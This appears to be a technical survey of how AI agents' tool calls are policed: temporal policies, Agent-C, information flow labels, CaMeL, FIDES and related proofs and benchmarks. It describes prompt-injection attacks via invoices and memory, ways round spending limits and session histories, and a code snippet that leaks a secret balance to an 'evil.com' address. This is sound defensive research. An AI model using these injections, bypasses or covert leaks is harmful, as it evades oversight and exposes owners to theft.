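AWS's *Authoring temporal policies* describes three kinds of event. A `request` event records a call submitted for authorization, with its arguments. A `response` event records that the tool returned successfully and includes its output. An `error` event records that a policy denied the call or that the tool failed.

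If *t* is the time of the current request and *w* the length of the window, the two basic operators have these meanings:

- `formerly within w B`: event *B* occurred at some time *t*′ with *t* − *w* ≤ *t*′ ≤ *t*.
- `A since within w B`: event *B* occurred at such a time *t*′, and condition *A* has held ever since.

The language also has operators for counting events, counting distinct values and adding up amounts. InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* explains that the language defines all of these in terms of a smaller core, a subset of metric first-order temporal logic. Hublet and colleagues study this logic, which combines statements about past and future with time limits and with variables for data such as payees and amounts.

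Suppose `request_approval` takes the payee and the amount as separate arguments. The approval rule, slightly shortened, might then be:

```
permit (principal, action == Action::"transfer_funds", resource)
when temporal {
  !Action::"transfer_funds"::response{
      input.payee: context.input.payee,
      input.amount: context.input.amount }
  since within 1h
  Action::"request_approval"::response{
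      input.payee: context.input.payee,
      input.amount: context.input.amount,
      output.approved: true }
};
```

This rule permits a transfer if the owner approved the same payee and amount within the last hour and no such transfer has succeeded since. It checks `output.approved`, which the approval tool returns. If it checked an input field instead, the agent could approve its own payment by supplying the right value.

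Cedar still makes the final decision. Before each decision, the Dogwood interpreter evaluates the temporal condition against the recorded events and puts the result in a field of the request's context. Cedar reads this field like any other. The proofs that Cedar denies by default and gives forbid policies priority therefore still apply to this last step, but the guarantee now also depends on the interpreter and the record of events.

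Small details of these rules can change their meaning. The current request counts as part of the history, so a rule that forbids a transfer if there was a transfer request in the last minute would block every transfer, including the first. Running totals can also be wrong, because the underlying logic works with sets, in which equal elements count only once, so two payments of €400 could add up to €400. In *The MonPoly Monitoring Tool*, Basin, Klaedtke and Zălinescu solve this by attaching to each amount its position in the history, and AWS's examples do the same.

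### Three transfers at once

Suppose a policy limits an agent's transfers to $5,000, and the agent proposes three transfers of $2,000 at the same time. All three requests reach the policy engine before the bank has completed any of them. InfoQ reports this example from AWS's announcement. The result depends on whether the rule adds up responses or requests:

| Transfer | Total of earlier responses | Decision | Total of requests, including this one | Decision |
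|---|---|---|---|---|
| First | $0 | Allow | $2,000 | Allow |
| Second | $0 | Allow | $4,000 | Allow |
| Third | $0 | Allow | $6,000 | Deny |

With responses, $6,000 leaves the account. Adding the current amount to the total of responses doesn't help, because each transfer would then count as $2,000. With requests, the engine counts the money before it leaves, so that

money paid ≤ money requested and allowed ≤ $5,000

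holds even while transfers are in progress. The disadvantage is that a transfer that passes the check but fails at the bank still uses up part of the limit.

The proof for the bookkeeping agent's €5,000 limit assumed that the harness finishes each check and update before it starts the next. An engine that counts requests can meet this condition without waiting for the bank, as long as it records each request before deciding the next. AgentCore allows only one authorization request at a time in each session.

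The approval rule above has the same weakness because it treats an approval as used only after a transfer has succeeded. If the agent proposes the approved transfer twice, and the second request arrives before the first gets a response, the rule allows both. Replacing `response` with `request` would make every transfer block itself. A safer rule enforces the automaton's invariant by allowing a transfer only if the number of matching transfer requests, including the current one, is at most the number of matching approvals.

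AWS's *Temporal policies* advises developers to wait for the response to one call before issuing another that depends on it. This protects the firm only if the harness enforces it, since the model may propose both calls together. Privy's *using stateful policies* describes the same problem in a product that signs cryptocurrency transactions, where several simultaneous requests can pass before any is added to the running totals, because Privy updates those totals only after signing. Privy therefore describes the feature as protection against disasters rather than strict enforcement, and recommends a separate limit on each transaction.

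### What rules about history cost

#### Less analysis

Cedar's solver can't analyse temporal conditions. According to InfoQ, this is why AWS made Dogwood a separate language instead of extending Cedar. Analysing a Cedar policy involves one request and a finite set of records, whereas analysing a temporal policy can involve sequences of any length.

AWS's examples for a private-banking agent show why the loss matters. One policy is supposed to limit trades to $60,000 in a session, but it adds up a field from requests for market prices, so trades never count towards the limit. Another is supposed to stop the agent from trading after 15 minutes without contact with the human adviser, but as published it permits trading only if there has been no contact in the last 15 minutes.

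The most serious mistake appears only when the policies are combined. The trade policies are all permit policies, and a trade is allowed if any one of them applies. The approval policy permits any trade below $25,000, so an agent could make any number of $24,000 trades, even if they violate the policies on spending limits and fresh prices. In AWS's reference documentation, the spending limit is a forbid policy, which avoids this problem.

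These mistakes are easy to miss when reviewing the text, but a solver could find the last one quickly by searching for an allowed trade that exceeds the limit. Help Net Security's *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* (2026) describes a newer service that uses automated reasoning to flag conflicting rules. It is unclear from the announcement whether this covers temporal conditions. Greenlight also shows which recorded calls a proposed rule would have blocked. That could have exposed the reversed 15-minute rule, although a replay covers only recorded histories.

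#### A record that must be complete

A rule about past calls depends on a reliable record of those calls. AWS intends Dogwood's reference interpreter only for exploring and testing the language. According to InfoQ, a production system must add trustworthy timestamps, authenticated events, consistent names for fields and actions, and durable storage, and it must keep different customers' histories apart. Evaluation can also take longer as the record grows.

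An event missing from the record can make a rule too strict or too lenient. A rule that requires an approval blocks the payment if the approval wasn't recorded, which is inconvenient but safe. But a rule against outside contact after the agent opens the payroll folder allows the email if the record doesn't show that the folder was opened. Rules that depend on something *not* having happened, including all spending limits, therefore need a complete record.

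Strands Box, AWS's sandbox for agents, addresses part of this problem by keeping one history for shell commands, Python code, tool calls and network traffic. A rule can then block a web request after the agent has read a customer file, whichever program read it. But Help Net Security reports that files the user grants directly to the agent never appear in this history. The agent can therefore read a customer file granted this way without triggering the rule. To prevent this, the user has to withhold direct access to such files, so that the agent can reach them only through the monitored interpreters. Brooker acknowledges that these interpreters add complex code to the trusted base, and that a bug in them could let an agent bypass the policy.

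Even with a complete record, a rule against outside contact blocks harmless messages along with harmful ones, because it applies once the agent has read the folder, whether or not a message contains anything from it. Data labels can be used to track whether a message contains data from the folder.

#### Limits that start again

AgentCore keeps a separate history for each session and combines the session identifier with the user's identity, so two users can't share a history. However, the caller supplies the session identifier, and a new identifier starts an empty history. An agent that can choose its own identifier could therefore get around a limit by starting a new session. AWS warns that such a limit is not a security control against a determined caller. The harness should set the identifier in code that the model can't influence, and a limit that must hold across sessions needs a total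 stored elsewhere, such as at the bank.

Adding or changing a temporal policy also ends all active sessions, because the old history may not fit the new rules. The next session starts with an empty record, so if an owner lowers the spending limit in the afternoon, the agent may be able to spend the full new amount on top of what it spent that morning.

Time windows can't exceed 24 hours, so AgentCore can't use them to enforce a weekly limit. The windows are also rolling and don't follow calendar days. Fixed periods are on Dogwood's roadmap.

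### Looking ahead with Agent-C

Dogwood's conditions depend only on the past. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) presents Agent-C, which also checks whether the agent can still meet its remaining obligations. Its specifications include statements such as *Before* (a call requires an earlier one) and *After* (a call requires a later one).

One Agent-C example is a customer service agent for an online shop. Before reading an order's details, the agent must look up the customer by email address, and that customer must own the order. Agent-C gets the owner's identity from the shop's own records through a read-only function, so the model can't satisfy the rule by making up a fact, as it could with the refund policy that took the order date from the model's arguments.

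When the model proposes a call, Agent-C adds it to the trace, which is the list of calls so far with their inputs and outputs. It then asks the solver Z3 whether

⟦τ⟧ ∧ Ψ

is satisfiable, where ⟦τ⟧ says that the run begins with the trace τ, and Ψ is the specification. If it is, at least one way of continuing the run obeys all the rules, and the call can go ahead. If the rules say that the agent must close every file it opens, Agent-C allows it to open one, because it can still close the file later. When the model tries to finish, Agent-C adds an event that rules out further calls. The formula is then satisfiable only if the file is closed.

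If a call fails the check, Agent-C has the model generate another. With open-weight models, it can restart from the beginning of the call without processing the whole prompt again. With commercial models, whose makers don't expose the necessary probabilities, it has to prompt the model again from the beginning. After a fixed number of failures, it records an error instead of making a call.

Kamath and colleagues prove that if a trace obeys the specification and Agent-C returns a tool call, the trace with that call added also obeys it. The proof relies on the algorithm returning a call only after the solver has found the formula satisfiable. If the solver doesn't answer in time, the call doesn't go ahead. The theorem assumes that no other process changes the tools' data, so it wouldn't cover an order whose owner changes between the check and the call. They also describe executing only one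 call at a time and leave out parallel transfers.

They tested Agent-C on τ-bench, a benchmark with 115 retail tasks and 50 airline tasks. In this table, "completed" means that the agent finished the task without breaking the policy:

| Model and tasks | Obeyed policy, without → with Agent-C | Completed, without → with Agent-C |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5, retail | 93.0% → 100% | 76.5% → 80.5% |
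| Claude Sonnet 4.5, airline | 70.0% → 100% | 42.0% → 43.5% |
| GPT-5, retail | 91.9% → 100% | 71.0% → 73.6% |
| GPT-5, airline | 71.3% → 100% | 38.0% → 42.8% |
| Qwen3-32B, retail | 37.7% → 100% | 25.5% → 53.3% |
| Qwen3-32B, airline | 35.3% → 100% | 17.3% → 35.8% |

The theorem predicts the scores of 100%, so they mainly confirm that the implementation works. The higher completion rates are more interesting, because a strict check could have made the agent less useful. Apparently, the model often responds to a rejected call by doing the missing step and carrying on. The gains are small for the stronger models. On the airline tasks with Qwen3-32B, an older rule system, AgentSpec, had a slightly higher completion rate (38.7%), but the agent broke the policy in about a fifth of the runs with AgentSpec.

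Kamath and colleagues also wrote 17 retail tasks in which the user tries to get the agent to do something forbidden, and listed the harmful calls for each by hand. Claude Sonnet 4.5 made those calls in five of the 17 tasks without Agent-C and in none with it. However, the checks increased the average time for an ordinary task with Qwen3-32B from 333 seconds to 480.

### Why a bill may never be paid

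Agent-C can keep a session from counting as properly finished while an obligation is outstanding, but it can't make the model meet the obligation. If the model stops too early, the session ends in an error state, with the file still open or the bill still unpaid, for example.

Under the arbitrary-output assumption, no monitor can guarantee that every invoice is eventually paid. The proof would have to cover a model that calls `get_balance` at every step and one that declares the task finished at once, and neither ever proposes a payment. To prove the claim, one would have to assume that the model eventually proposes the right payment. Liveness properties are on Dogwood's roadmap, but this obstacle will remain for any rule that relies on the model to act.

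The harness can guarantee that its loop stops, because it controls whether the model is called again. Let *N* be the maximum number of steps and *k* the number already taken. Then *N* − *k* is a whole number that falls by one at each step, and the loop ends when it reaches zero. Each step must also end, so the harness needs a time limit for every model response and every tool call. If each of 50 steps allows up to 60 seconds for the model response and 30 seconds for a tool call, the loop runs for no more than 75 minutes.

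This makes a useful liveness guarantee possible if the harness may also act on its own. When the loop ends, ordinary code can check the invoices the owner asked the agent to pay and report to the owner any that lack a confirmed payment. One can then prove that each invoice is eventually either paid or reported, whatever the model does. The proof assumes that the computer keeps running, that the message reaches the owner and that the payment records are correct. Unlike Schneider's monitor, the harness here causes an action, and it can do so safely because a report needs no judgment about whom to pay.

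### When a call only half succeeds

Records of payments can be wrong because the outcome of a tool call is sometimes unclear. Suppose the harness sends the bank a transfer of €412.80 to a supplier, the bank carries it out, and the connection breaks before the confirmation arrives. The harness stops waiting after 30 seconds, but it has no way to distinguish this from a request that never reached the bank. If it tries again, it may pay twice, and if it doesn't, the supplier may get nothing.

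The approval rule in Dogwood permits a second payment in this case if the agent tries again within the hour. A tool that returns an error produces an `error` event but no `response`, so the approval still counts as unused. A €5,000 limit on the total requested does count the first attempt, so the loss stays within the limit, but two payments of €412.80 are well below it.

*Verified Tool Calls Improve LLM Agent Reliability Under Non-Atomic Failures* (2026) proposes a wrapper around each tool that checks whether the intended effect has occurred, both after a call and before any retry. The wrapper also attaches an idempotency key, a unique label that lets the receiving system recognise a repeated request and carry it out only once. In a simulation with injected failures, the wrapper greatly reduced duplicate actions, and agents completed about as many tasks as without it.

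An idempotency key gives the strongest protection if the harness creates it when the owner approves a payment and reuses it for every attempt. Each approval can then result in at most one payment, however many requests arrive in parallel or after a timeout. This fixes both weaknesses of the approval rule, but only if the bank honours the keys, so the bank's software becomes part of the trusted base. The model must not be able to choose the key, because the bank would treat a retry with a new key as a new payment.

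#### Checking what a tool returns

A harness can also check a tool's result before relying on it. Liu, Peng and colleagues (2026), in *ToolGate*, give each tool a contract in the notation that Tony Hoare introduced in 1969 for reasoning about programs:

{*P*} *t* {*Q*}

The harness may call a tool *t* only if the precondition *P* holds in the harness's trusted state, a typed list of facts that have passed earlier checks. When the tool returns a result, the harness tests the postcondition *Q*. If *Q* holds, the harness updates the trusted state. Otherwise, it discards the result and leaves the state unchanged.

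This works well for tools that only retrieve information. In tests with GPT-5.2 on managing code repositories, ToolGate completed 45.5% of tasks, compared with 39.4% for the best alternative. These figures measure task completion, not how often the contracts prevented harm. A plausible but wrong bank balance would still pass a postcondition that checks types, ranges and format.

Discarding the result is dangerous when the tool changes something. If the bank makes the payment but returns a damaged receipt, the receipt fails the check and the trusted state still lists the invoice as unpaid. The precondition for payment still holds, so the agent can pay again.

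The approval automaton needs a third state, SENT, to handle this. The monitor enters it as soon as it lets a transfer through, and blocks further transfers under the same approval until the bank confirms the outcome. The automaton then returns to WAITING if the bank made the payment, or to APPROVED if the bank rejected it. A timeout or a damaged receipt leaves it in SENT. A search of the account that finds no payment should also leave it there, because a payment that the bank is still processing may not appear in the account yet.

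## Tracking where data came from and where it may go

Information flow control tracks data, so it can block messages that contain payroll data without blocking all the others. The harness labels each piece of data by secrecy or trust, works out labels for everything derived from it, and allows or blocks each tool call according to the labels of its arguments. Labels can also record whether an account number came from the firm's records or from a stranger's email, information that a Cedar request lacks.

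### How labels combine

The simplest scheme labels data as public or secret, and as trusted or untrusted. A ⊑ B means that data labeled A may flow to places labeled B. Public ⊑ secret, because data that anyone may see can safely go where secrets go. Trusted ⊑ untrusted, because a program can use trusted data wherever untrusted data would do. When a program computes a value from two others, the result's label is the join (⊔) of their labels, which is the lowest label that both may flow to. The result is secret if either source is secret, and untrusted if either is untrusted.

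In the bookkeeping agent, the firm's balance is trusted and secret, and the supplier's invoice is untrusted and public. A payment reference that uses data from both is untrusted and secret.

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) also describes finer labels. A secrecy label can be the set of people who may read the data, and the join of two labels keeps only the people in both sets. If the owner and the accountant may read the balance, and the owner and the supplier may read the invoice, only the owner may read a text based on both.

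They give two basic rules for tool calls. A consequential call, such as a payment, needs a trusted label on the choice of tool and on every argument. A call that sends data needs every recipient to be an allowed reader of that data. The second rule limits what an attacker can learn, but it doesn't prevent prompt injection, since instructions injected into an invoice can still make the agent send something.

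### Noninterference as a comparison of two runs

Let *n* be the highest label an observer can see. Write *s* ∼ₙ *t* if the states *s* and *t* agree on every value whose label may flow to *n*. A deterministic program *P* satisfies noninterference if, for every *n*, *s* and *t*,

*s* ∼ₙ *t* ⇒ *P*(*s*) ∼ₙ *P*(*t*)

In the earlier example of the payment reference, *n* is "public" and the two starting states differ only in the balance.

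Barthe explains that the same formula covers trust. If *n* is "trusted" and two states differ only in the text of the invoice, both must produce the same trusted results. If the harness makes only payments labeled trusted, changing the invoice text cannot alter any payment.

Schneider's result shows that no monitor can enforce exactly this property by watching a single run. Label tracking enforces a stricter property by blocking any call whose data *may* have depended on a secret, even if a different secret would have led to the same call. It therefore also stops some harmless runs.

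A program can reveal a secret without copying it. Suppose it sends the supplier a greeting only if the balance exceeds €10,000. The greeting contains nothing secret, but the supplier can infer from its arrival that the balance exceeds €10,000. Trackers therefore also keep a label for the current point in the program, called the program-counter label. Inside a branch, this label includes the label of the condition, so the greeting counts as secret.

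### Why reading the invoice taints the model

In an ordinary program, a tracker can follow each value from one line to the next. Nobody can do this inside a language model, because any part of the output may depend on any part of the input through billions of parameters. If the model proposes a payment of €412.80, the harness can't tell whether the figure came from the owner or the invoice. A hidden instruction may even be why the model proposed a payment at all.

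Costa and colleagues label every response with the join of the labels of everything the model has read. This is safe but restrictive, because one untrusted email makes every later proposal untrusted. They mention a less restrictive approach that finds the messages that influenced a response and regenerates it from those messages alone.

With the strict rule, the bookkeeping agent can't pay an invoice after reading it. Costa and colleagues measured the effect on AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, travel, banking and Slack tasks with planted injections. An ordinary agent using GPT-4o completed 98.8% of the banking tasks without label checks and 37.5% with them.

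### CaMeL

In 2023 Willison proposed using two models to avoid this problem. A privileged model plans and calls tools but never reads untrusted data, while a quarantined model reads untrusted data but has no tools. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) presents CaMeL, which builds on this idea by having the privileged model write a program. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) analyses CaMeL's design and reruns its tests.

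Suppose the bookkeeping agent also has a tool `supplier_account`, which looks up an account in the firm's own records. From the owner's request, the privileged model might write:

```
mail    = read_email(sender="Paper supplier", date=today)
bill    = quarantined_llm("Find the amount and the invoice number",
                          mail.body)
account = supplier_account("Paper supplier")
transfer_funds(account, bill.amount, reference=bill.number)
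```

The model writes this program before anyone opens the email. An interpreter for a restricted form of Python then runs it line by line, recording where each value came from and who may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks this information against a policy for that tool. The policy for `transfer_funds` might require the account number to come from the firm's records. Girrens and Wang (2026) point out in *SPA* that such policies can express more than simple labels, but the guarantee then depends on someone writing each policy correctly.

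#### What the invoice can still change

| What the attacker puts in the invoice | What happens |
|---|---|
| An instruction to send the inbox to an outside address | Nothing, because the program has no such step and the quarantined model has no tools |
| A notice that the supplier has changed banks | Nothing, because the program takes the account from the firm's records |
| An instruction to put the balance in the reference | The balance stays secret, because the quarantined model never receives it |
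| A false amount of €4,128.00 | The program tries to pay €4,128.00 |
| A false invoice number | The false number appears in the payment reference |

The attacker can print the false amount on the invoice without any hidden instruction, and a quarantined model that works perfectly will extract it. Girrens and Wang make the same point about a false account number. That attack would work here if the program took the account number from the invoice.

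A policy that requires a trusted amount would stop the false payment, but it would also stop the correct one, since €412.80 and €4,128.00 come from the same untrusted email. If the policy accepts untrusted amounts, the attacker can choose any amount up to the limit, which is €500 under the earlier Cedar policy. To distinguish correct amounts from false ones, the program needs a trusted fact to compare with the invoice, such as a purchase order in the firm's records.

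A fixed program also protects less when the owner asks the agent to take its steps from the data. One AgentDojo banking task asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions. In tests by Garby and colleagues, CaMeL's privileged model sometimes wrote a loop with a branch for each tool, so the file's contents could determine which tools ran. With the policy checks switched off, an injection succeeded through such a loop, even though the privileged model never read the injected text.

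### FIDES

FIDES, built by Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, lets the planning model choose each step after receiving the results of earlier ones. If a tool returns data that would taint the model's context, FIDES stores the data in a variable and gives the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to another tool or query a quarantined model about the variable's contents. It can also open the variable, but the planning model's context then takes on the data's label.

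FIDES can restrict the quarantined model's answer to yes or no, or to a short list of options. A policy may then let the planning model see the answer and still take consequential actions, because one bit is too little to carry an injected instruction. Costa and colleagues did not use this feature in their main tests.

FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy, a confidentiality property weaker than noninterference. It covers the copying of secrets but not the decisions that depend on them, so an observer who sees which tools the agent calls can still learn something about the secrets. Costa and colleagues accept this because full noninterference would block almost every publicly visible action after the agent has read a secret.

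### How many tasks survive the checks

In the AgentDojo tests with GPT-4o, 152 injections succeeded against an ordinary agent. Adding FIDES's variables without its policy checks reduced that to 21, and adding the checks reduced it to zero. These counts exclude cases that Costa and colleagues found the benchmark had scored incorrectly. The team also labeled as untrusted every data field that any attack in the benchmark used. The result therefore shows that the checks work when the labels are right, but not that an engineer would choose the right labels for a real mailbox.

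Two studies from 2026 provide newer measurements. Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL with current models on AgentDojo's banking tasks. Girrens and Wang tested their own system, SPA, on all of AgentDojo. Like CaMeL, SPA plans before reading any data.

| System and model | Tasks | Completed, checks off → on | Successful attacks with checks on |
|---|---|---|---|
| FIDES, GPT-4o (2025) | Banking | 65.0% → 52.5% | None |
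| CaMeL, GPT-5.2 (2026) | Banking | 66.7% → 37.5% | None in 231 completed runs |
| CaMeL, MiMo-v2.5 (2026) | Banking | 70.8% → 37.5% | None in 357 completed runs |
| SPA (2026) | All areas | 53.0% → 29.0% | 0.0% |

The CaMeL figures are rough because the banking suite has only 16 different tasks and the 95% confidence intervals extend more than 20 percentage points either way, but the direction is the same in every row. Girrens and Wang attribute most of SPA's loss to checks that stop untrusted results from reaching actions that need trusted data. Many legitimate tasks need to pass such results to those actions.

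Better models recover some of the loss. With the same policies switched on, FIDES completed on average 8 percentage points more tasks than an ordinary agent when both used GPT-4o, and 16 points more when both used OpenAI's o1. But *PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) cites AgentDyn, a benchmark of changing tasks, on which CaMeL completed none.

The security figures also combine the protection from the fixed program with the protection from the label checks. Garby and colleagues found that in 97 of the banking suite's 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needs tool calls that a program written for the owner's task would never contain. The fixed program alone should defeat those attacks, so only the other 47 combinations test the label checks.

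### Leaks that a label tracker can miss

Garby and colleagues found two ways for secrets to escape CaMeL's tracking. One of them works with a program of this form:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > 10000: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL raises a variable's label only on a branch that the program takes. If the balance is above €10,000, `tmp` becomes false and secret, and the program skips the fourth line, so `rich` stays true and public and the email goes out. Otherwise, the program skips the third line, so `tmp` stays true and public. The fourth line then makes `rich` false, and no email goes out. In both cases `rich` is public, although it reveals whether the balance is above €10,000.

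The other leak comes from the loop that lets the privileged model retry after an error. This loop runs outside the tracker, so each attempt can reveal one bit, which is whether the policy blocked it. One bit is tolerable, but repeated attempts can reveal many. If the balance is below €1 million, 27 well-chosen yes-or-no answers are enough to find it to the cent.

An honest request is unlikely to lead to such programs, but a proof should cover them because the privileged model may make mistakes or be hostile. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) attributes part of the difficulty to Python, whose exceptions and ability to inspect running code make flows hard to analyse, and recommends a simpler language. SPA uses a simpler language in which programs can set each variable only once and can't use a variable outside the branch that created it, so the program above can't be written. SPA also checks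 both branches before anything runs.

### A theorem about the whole harness

Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language, the LLMbda calculus, in which every value and the conversation with the model have labels. Sending the model an untrusted email makes the conversation untrusted. Any code the model writes in response runs under the conversation's label, and everything that code computes keeps the label. A program can also start a separate conversation, ask a question there and discard the conversation. A developer can therefore write and change the split between a privileged and a quarantined model in a few lines of code.

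The interpreter stops a program that tries to add to a public conversation inside a branch that depends on a secret. This rule prevents the kind of leak that CaMeL allows, because a public record can't depend on which branch the program took.

A language model chooses its responses at random, so the theorem compares probabilities. Take two starting states that look the same to the observer, and let μ(*q*) and ν(*q*) be the probabilities that the observer sees result *q* from each. These may add up to less than one, because some runs never finish or the interpreter stops them. The theorem guarantees that there is a single function ω, with a total of at most one, such that for every *q*

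μ(*q*) ≤ ω(*q*) and ν(*q*) ≤ ω(*q*)

If every run finishes, μ and ν each add up to one, so both must equal ω, and the observer learns nothing. Otherwise, the distance between them is at most the average chance of not finishing:

½ Σ |μ(*q*) − ν(*q*)| ≤ ½ (chance of not finishing from *s* + chance of not finishing from *t*)

If 2% of runs fail to finish in both cases, for instance, the distance is at most 0.02.

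The proof uses an imaginary second interpreter that skips any computation as soon as its label becomes invisible to the observer and substitutes an empty value. This interpreter never uses hidden data, so it gives the same probabilities, ω, for both starting states. Skipping can only make a program finish more often, so ω is at least as large as μ and ν everywhere.

Lean has checked the proof, and the verified interpreter is also the program that calls the language model. The guarantee therefore covers every agent written in the language, including agents that write and run their own code. It still depends on correct labels for incoming data and correct checks in the tools. Garby and colleagues simulated the bank and its data inside the language, so connecting a real bank would add to the trusted base.

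### Releasing data on purpose

Dongol considers noninterference too strong for useful agents, which are designed to let untrusted content, such as an invoice, influence their actions and to disclose some private data. Practical systems therefore need to allow exceptions through declassification, which makes secret data less secret, and endorsement, which makes untrusted data trusted.

The LLMbda calculus has an explicit `endorse` operation, so a reviewer can find every exception in the program text. If a program endorses the amount on an invoice, the theorem about trust no longer protects that payment. Garby and colleagues prove that the theorem about secrecy still holds, so neither what an attacker writes on the invoice nor what the program endorses can cause the balance to leak. This is useful because a careless exception to one property could easily have weakened the other.

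Randori is an agent used to test endorsement. Before it receives any real data, its model does trial runs in a simulated world and selects which values the final program will endorse. With Qwen3.7-plus, Randori completed 75% of the banking tasks with endorsement and 62.5% without it.

The attacker succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs with endorsement, both times with the same attack. The user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The program endorsed the contents because the task required it. CaMeL's original evaluation included a successful attack on the same kind of task, which its developers place outside their threat model. Labels cannot be used to determine whether such a payment is legitimate, because the user delegated the decision to a file that the attacker could change.

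A program can limit an endorsement to a fixed list of values. If the quarantined model must choose one of eight categories for an email, the attacker controls at most three bits. An amount in whole cents up to €500 carries less than 16 bits, which is far too little to hold an injected instruction but enough to raise a bill from €412.80 to €500. The number of bits is therefore a poor measure of the possible loss, because a single bit can determine whether a large payment goes out.

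### Judging an agent against a reference agent

Endorsements are hard to write in advance when a model chooses the steps for each task. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (Dongol, 2026) proposes a criterion that needs no list of exceptions. It compares the deployed agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan under the same monitor, but whose model treats untrusted text only as data, never as instructions.

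For a run τ, let TE(τ) be the list of trusted inputs and effects in the order they occurred. The deployed agent has relative integrity if, for every run τ that has a counterpart with the same trusted inputs but a different list, the reference agent has a run τ̂ with

TE(τ̂) = TE(τ)

The counterpart condition identifies runs that were affected by something other than the trusted inputs, usually the attacker's text. The reference agent must start from a corresponding state, but it may read a different invoice.

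Dongol's example is an agent that has to pay the invoice in Bob's latest email, using the payee and the amount that the invoice states:

| Instruction in the invoice that the agent obeys | Verdict | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| None | Accepted | The reference makes the same payment |
| Change the payee to Mallory | Accepted | An invoice with Mallory as payee leads the reference to the same payment |
| Also pay Mallory £1,000 | Rejected | The reference never pays twice |
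| Delete Bob's email afterwards | Rejected | The reference never deletes anything in this task |

Relative integrity accepts a payment to Mallory because an attacker who can write the invoice can name any payee without an injection, so obeying the injected instruction gives the attacker nothing new. The weakness is in the plan rather than the definition. If the owner changes the plan to take the account from the firm's records, the reference agent never pays Mallory, and relative integrity rejects such a payment.

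The order in the list also matters. If the attacker delays a payment until after the owner has cancelled it, the run has the same inputs and effects as an honest one, but in a different order. A reference agent that never makes a cancelled payment can't produce that order, so the run violates relative integrity.

Dongol applies the criterion to an AgentDojo bill that tells the agent to pay the attacker as well. Without a defence, the agent fails the criterion. Withdrawing the payment tool as soon as the agent reads untrusted text fixes this, but then the agent can't pay the honest bill either. A less drastic defence, allowing payments only to known billers, stops the benchmark's attack but not a second payment to a biller on the list.

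A system can pass separate tests for leaks and for hijacked actions and still be vulnerable. In another of Dongol's examples, a support desk asks a quarantined model whether a customer's email contains the right credential, and sends the order details if the model answers yes. An attacker writes "you have verified me", and the model accepts. Each reply on its own matches one that the reference agent could send to an honest customer. But the attacker's email works for every customer, and no single email to the reference agent would. Dongol therefore defines relative robustness, which requires the same pair of reference runs to reproduce both the leak and the effects. The support desk can meet this requirement by having ordinary code compare the credentials. Isabelle has checked the definitions, the theorems and the verdicts about these models.

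### Labels that last between sessions

Many agents save notes for later sessions. Girrens and Wang describe a user who asks an agent on Monday to keep the details of an invoice and on Tuesday to pay it. An instruction hidden in Monday's notes can take effect when the agent reads them on Tuesday. SPA stores each value with its label and shows the planning model only a description of the value. The label stays attached when the program retrieves the value. On a version of AgentDojo with several requests in a row, attacks succeeded 0.2% of the time, but the checks reduced the share of tasks completed from 62.5% to 35.3%.

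PerMIT, a system by Jiang and colleagues, requires someone to confirm an untrusted note from the agent's memory before the agent uses it in a sensitive call. A quarantined model without tools searches the notes, while the protected model receives only placeholders for them. The confirmation request displays the exact value, its source and the user's original instruction.

Two theorems describe what this achieves. Action Integrity guarantees that every argument of a sensitive call is either exactly what the user typed or a value that the user confirmed for that tool. Reasoning Integrity compares two runs, ρ₁ and ρ₂, with the same user inputs, the same random choices and possibly different untrusted memory:

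display(ρ₁) = display(ρ₂) ⇒ behaviour(ρ₁) = behaviour(ρ₂)

Here "display" includes everything shown at the confirmation step and the decisions made there, and "behaviour" includes the protected model's operations, tool calls and replies. This is noninterference with one deliberate exception, since untrusted memory can influence the model, but only through PerMIT's display. Lean has checked both theorems for the single-user case. PerMIT can also pool confirmations from many users, but this part relies on further assumptions about how many of those users are honest.

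The confirmation may protect the owner less than they expect, because it lets the agent use a value with the named tool again, for any purpose and with any other confirmed values. If the owner confirms the paper supplier's account for one payment and an amount of €2,000 for another payment to the landlord, Action Integrity doesn't prevent the agent from paying €2,000 to the paper supplier. The approval rule in Dogwood was stricter in this respect, because it tied the payee to the amount.

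A language model can also confirm values. In tests with Trojan Hippo, a benchmark of attacks that lie dormant in an agent's memory, none of the attacks succeeded when PerMIT used models as verifiers. The theorems hold even if the verifier is careless, but in that case they guarantee only that the verifier approved the value.

### What to do when the labels block a call

A system that only blocks calls can leave an agent stuck, as the low completion rates suggest. Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026), in *APPA*, prove that an agent can't clear a missing trust requirement by reading more, because reading can only add restrictions to its context. Their system instead looks for a permitted way forward and offers it to the agent:

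- An authority, such as the owner or a fixed rule, approves the exact call. The approval changes no labels and can't be used for another call.
- A registered program makes a safe version of the data, for example by removing personal details.
- A registered check supplies a missing label for data from a tool that nobody has labelled yet.
- The agent reads the data in a temporary copy of the conversation, which can return only a value from a fixed set.

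The bookkeeping agent could have a temporary copy of itself read the invoice and return an amount in cents. Its main conversation would stay trusted, so it could continue with other work. An injection could still make the copy return a false but permitted amount, so the amount is still untrusted and the payment needs separate approval. A rule could approve the payment by comparing the amount with a purchase order, without interrupting the owner.

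Before allowing a call, APPA also accounts for what the tool will read. One of its test tools reads a confidential ledger and emails it in a single call. A monitor that checked only the labels the agent had before the call would detect the ledger only after the email had been sent.

In 1,320 test runs with APPA's protection, no attack succeeded, and agents completed between 64.2% and 91% of their tasks. Kravchenko and colleagues prove that every exception to noninterference stays within what engineers permitted in advance and appears in the log, but they don't claim noninterference in general. If engineers let a language model approve calls, security within those bounds depends on that model's decisions.

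### Checking flows before the code runs

CaMeL and FIDES check labels while the agent works. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) instead uses a compiler to do most of the checking before the agent's code runs. The agent writes its actions in Scala 3, with an experimental extension that records in each function's type which capabilities the function uses, such as file or network access.

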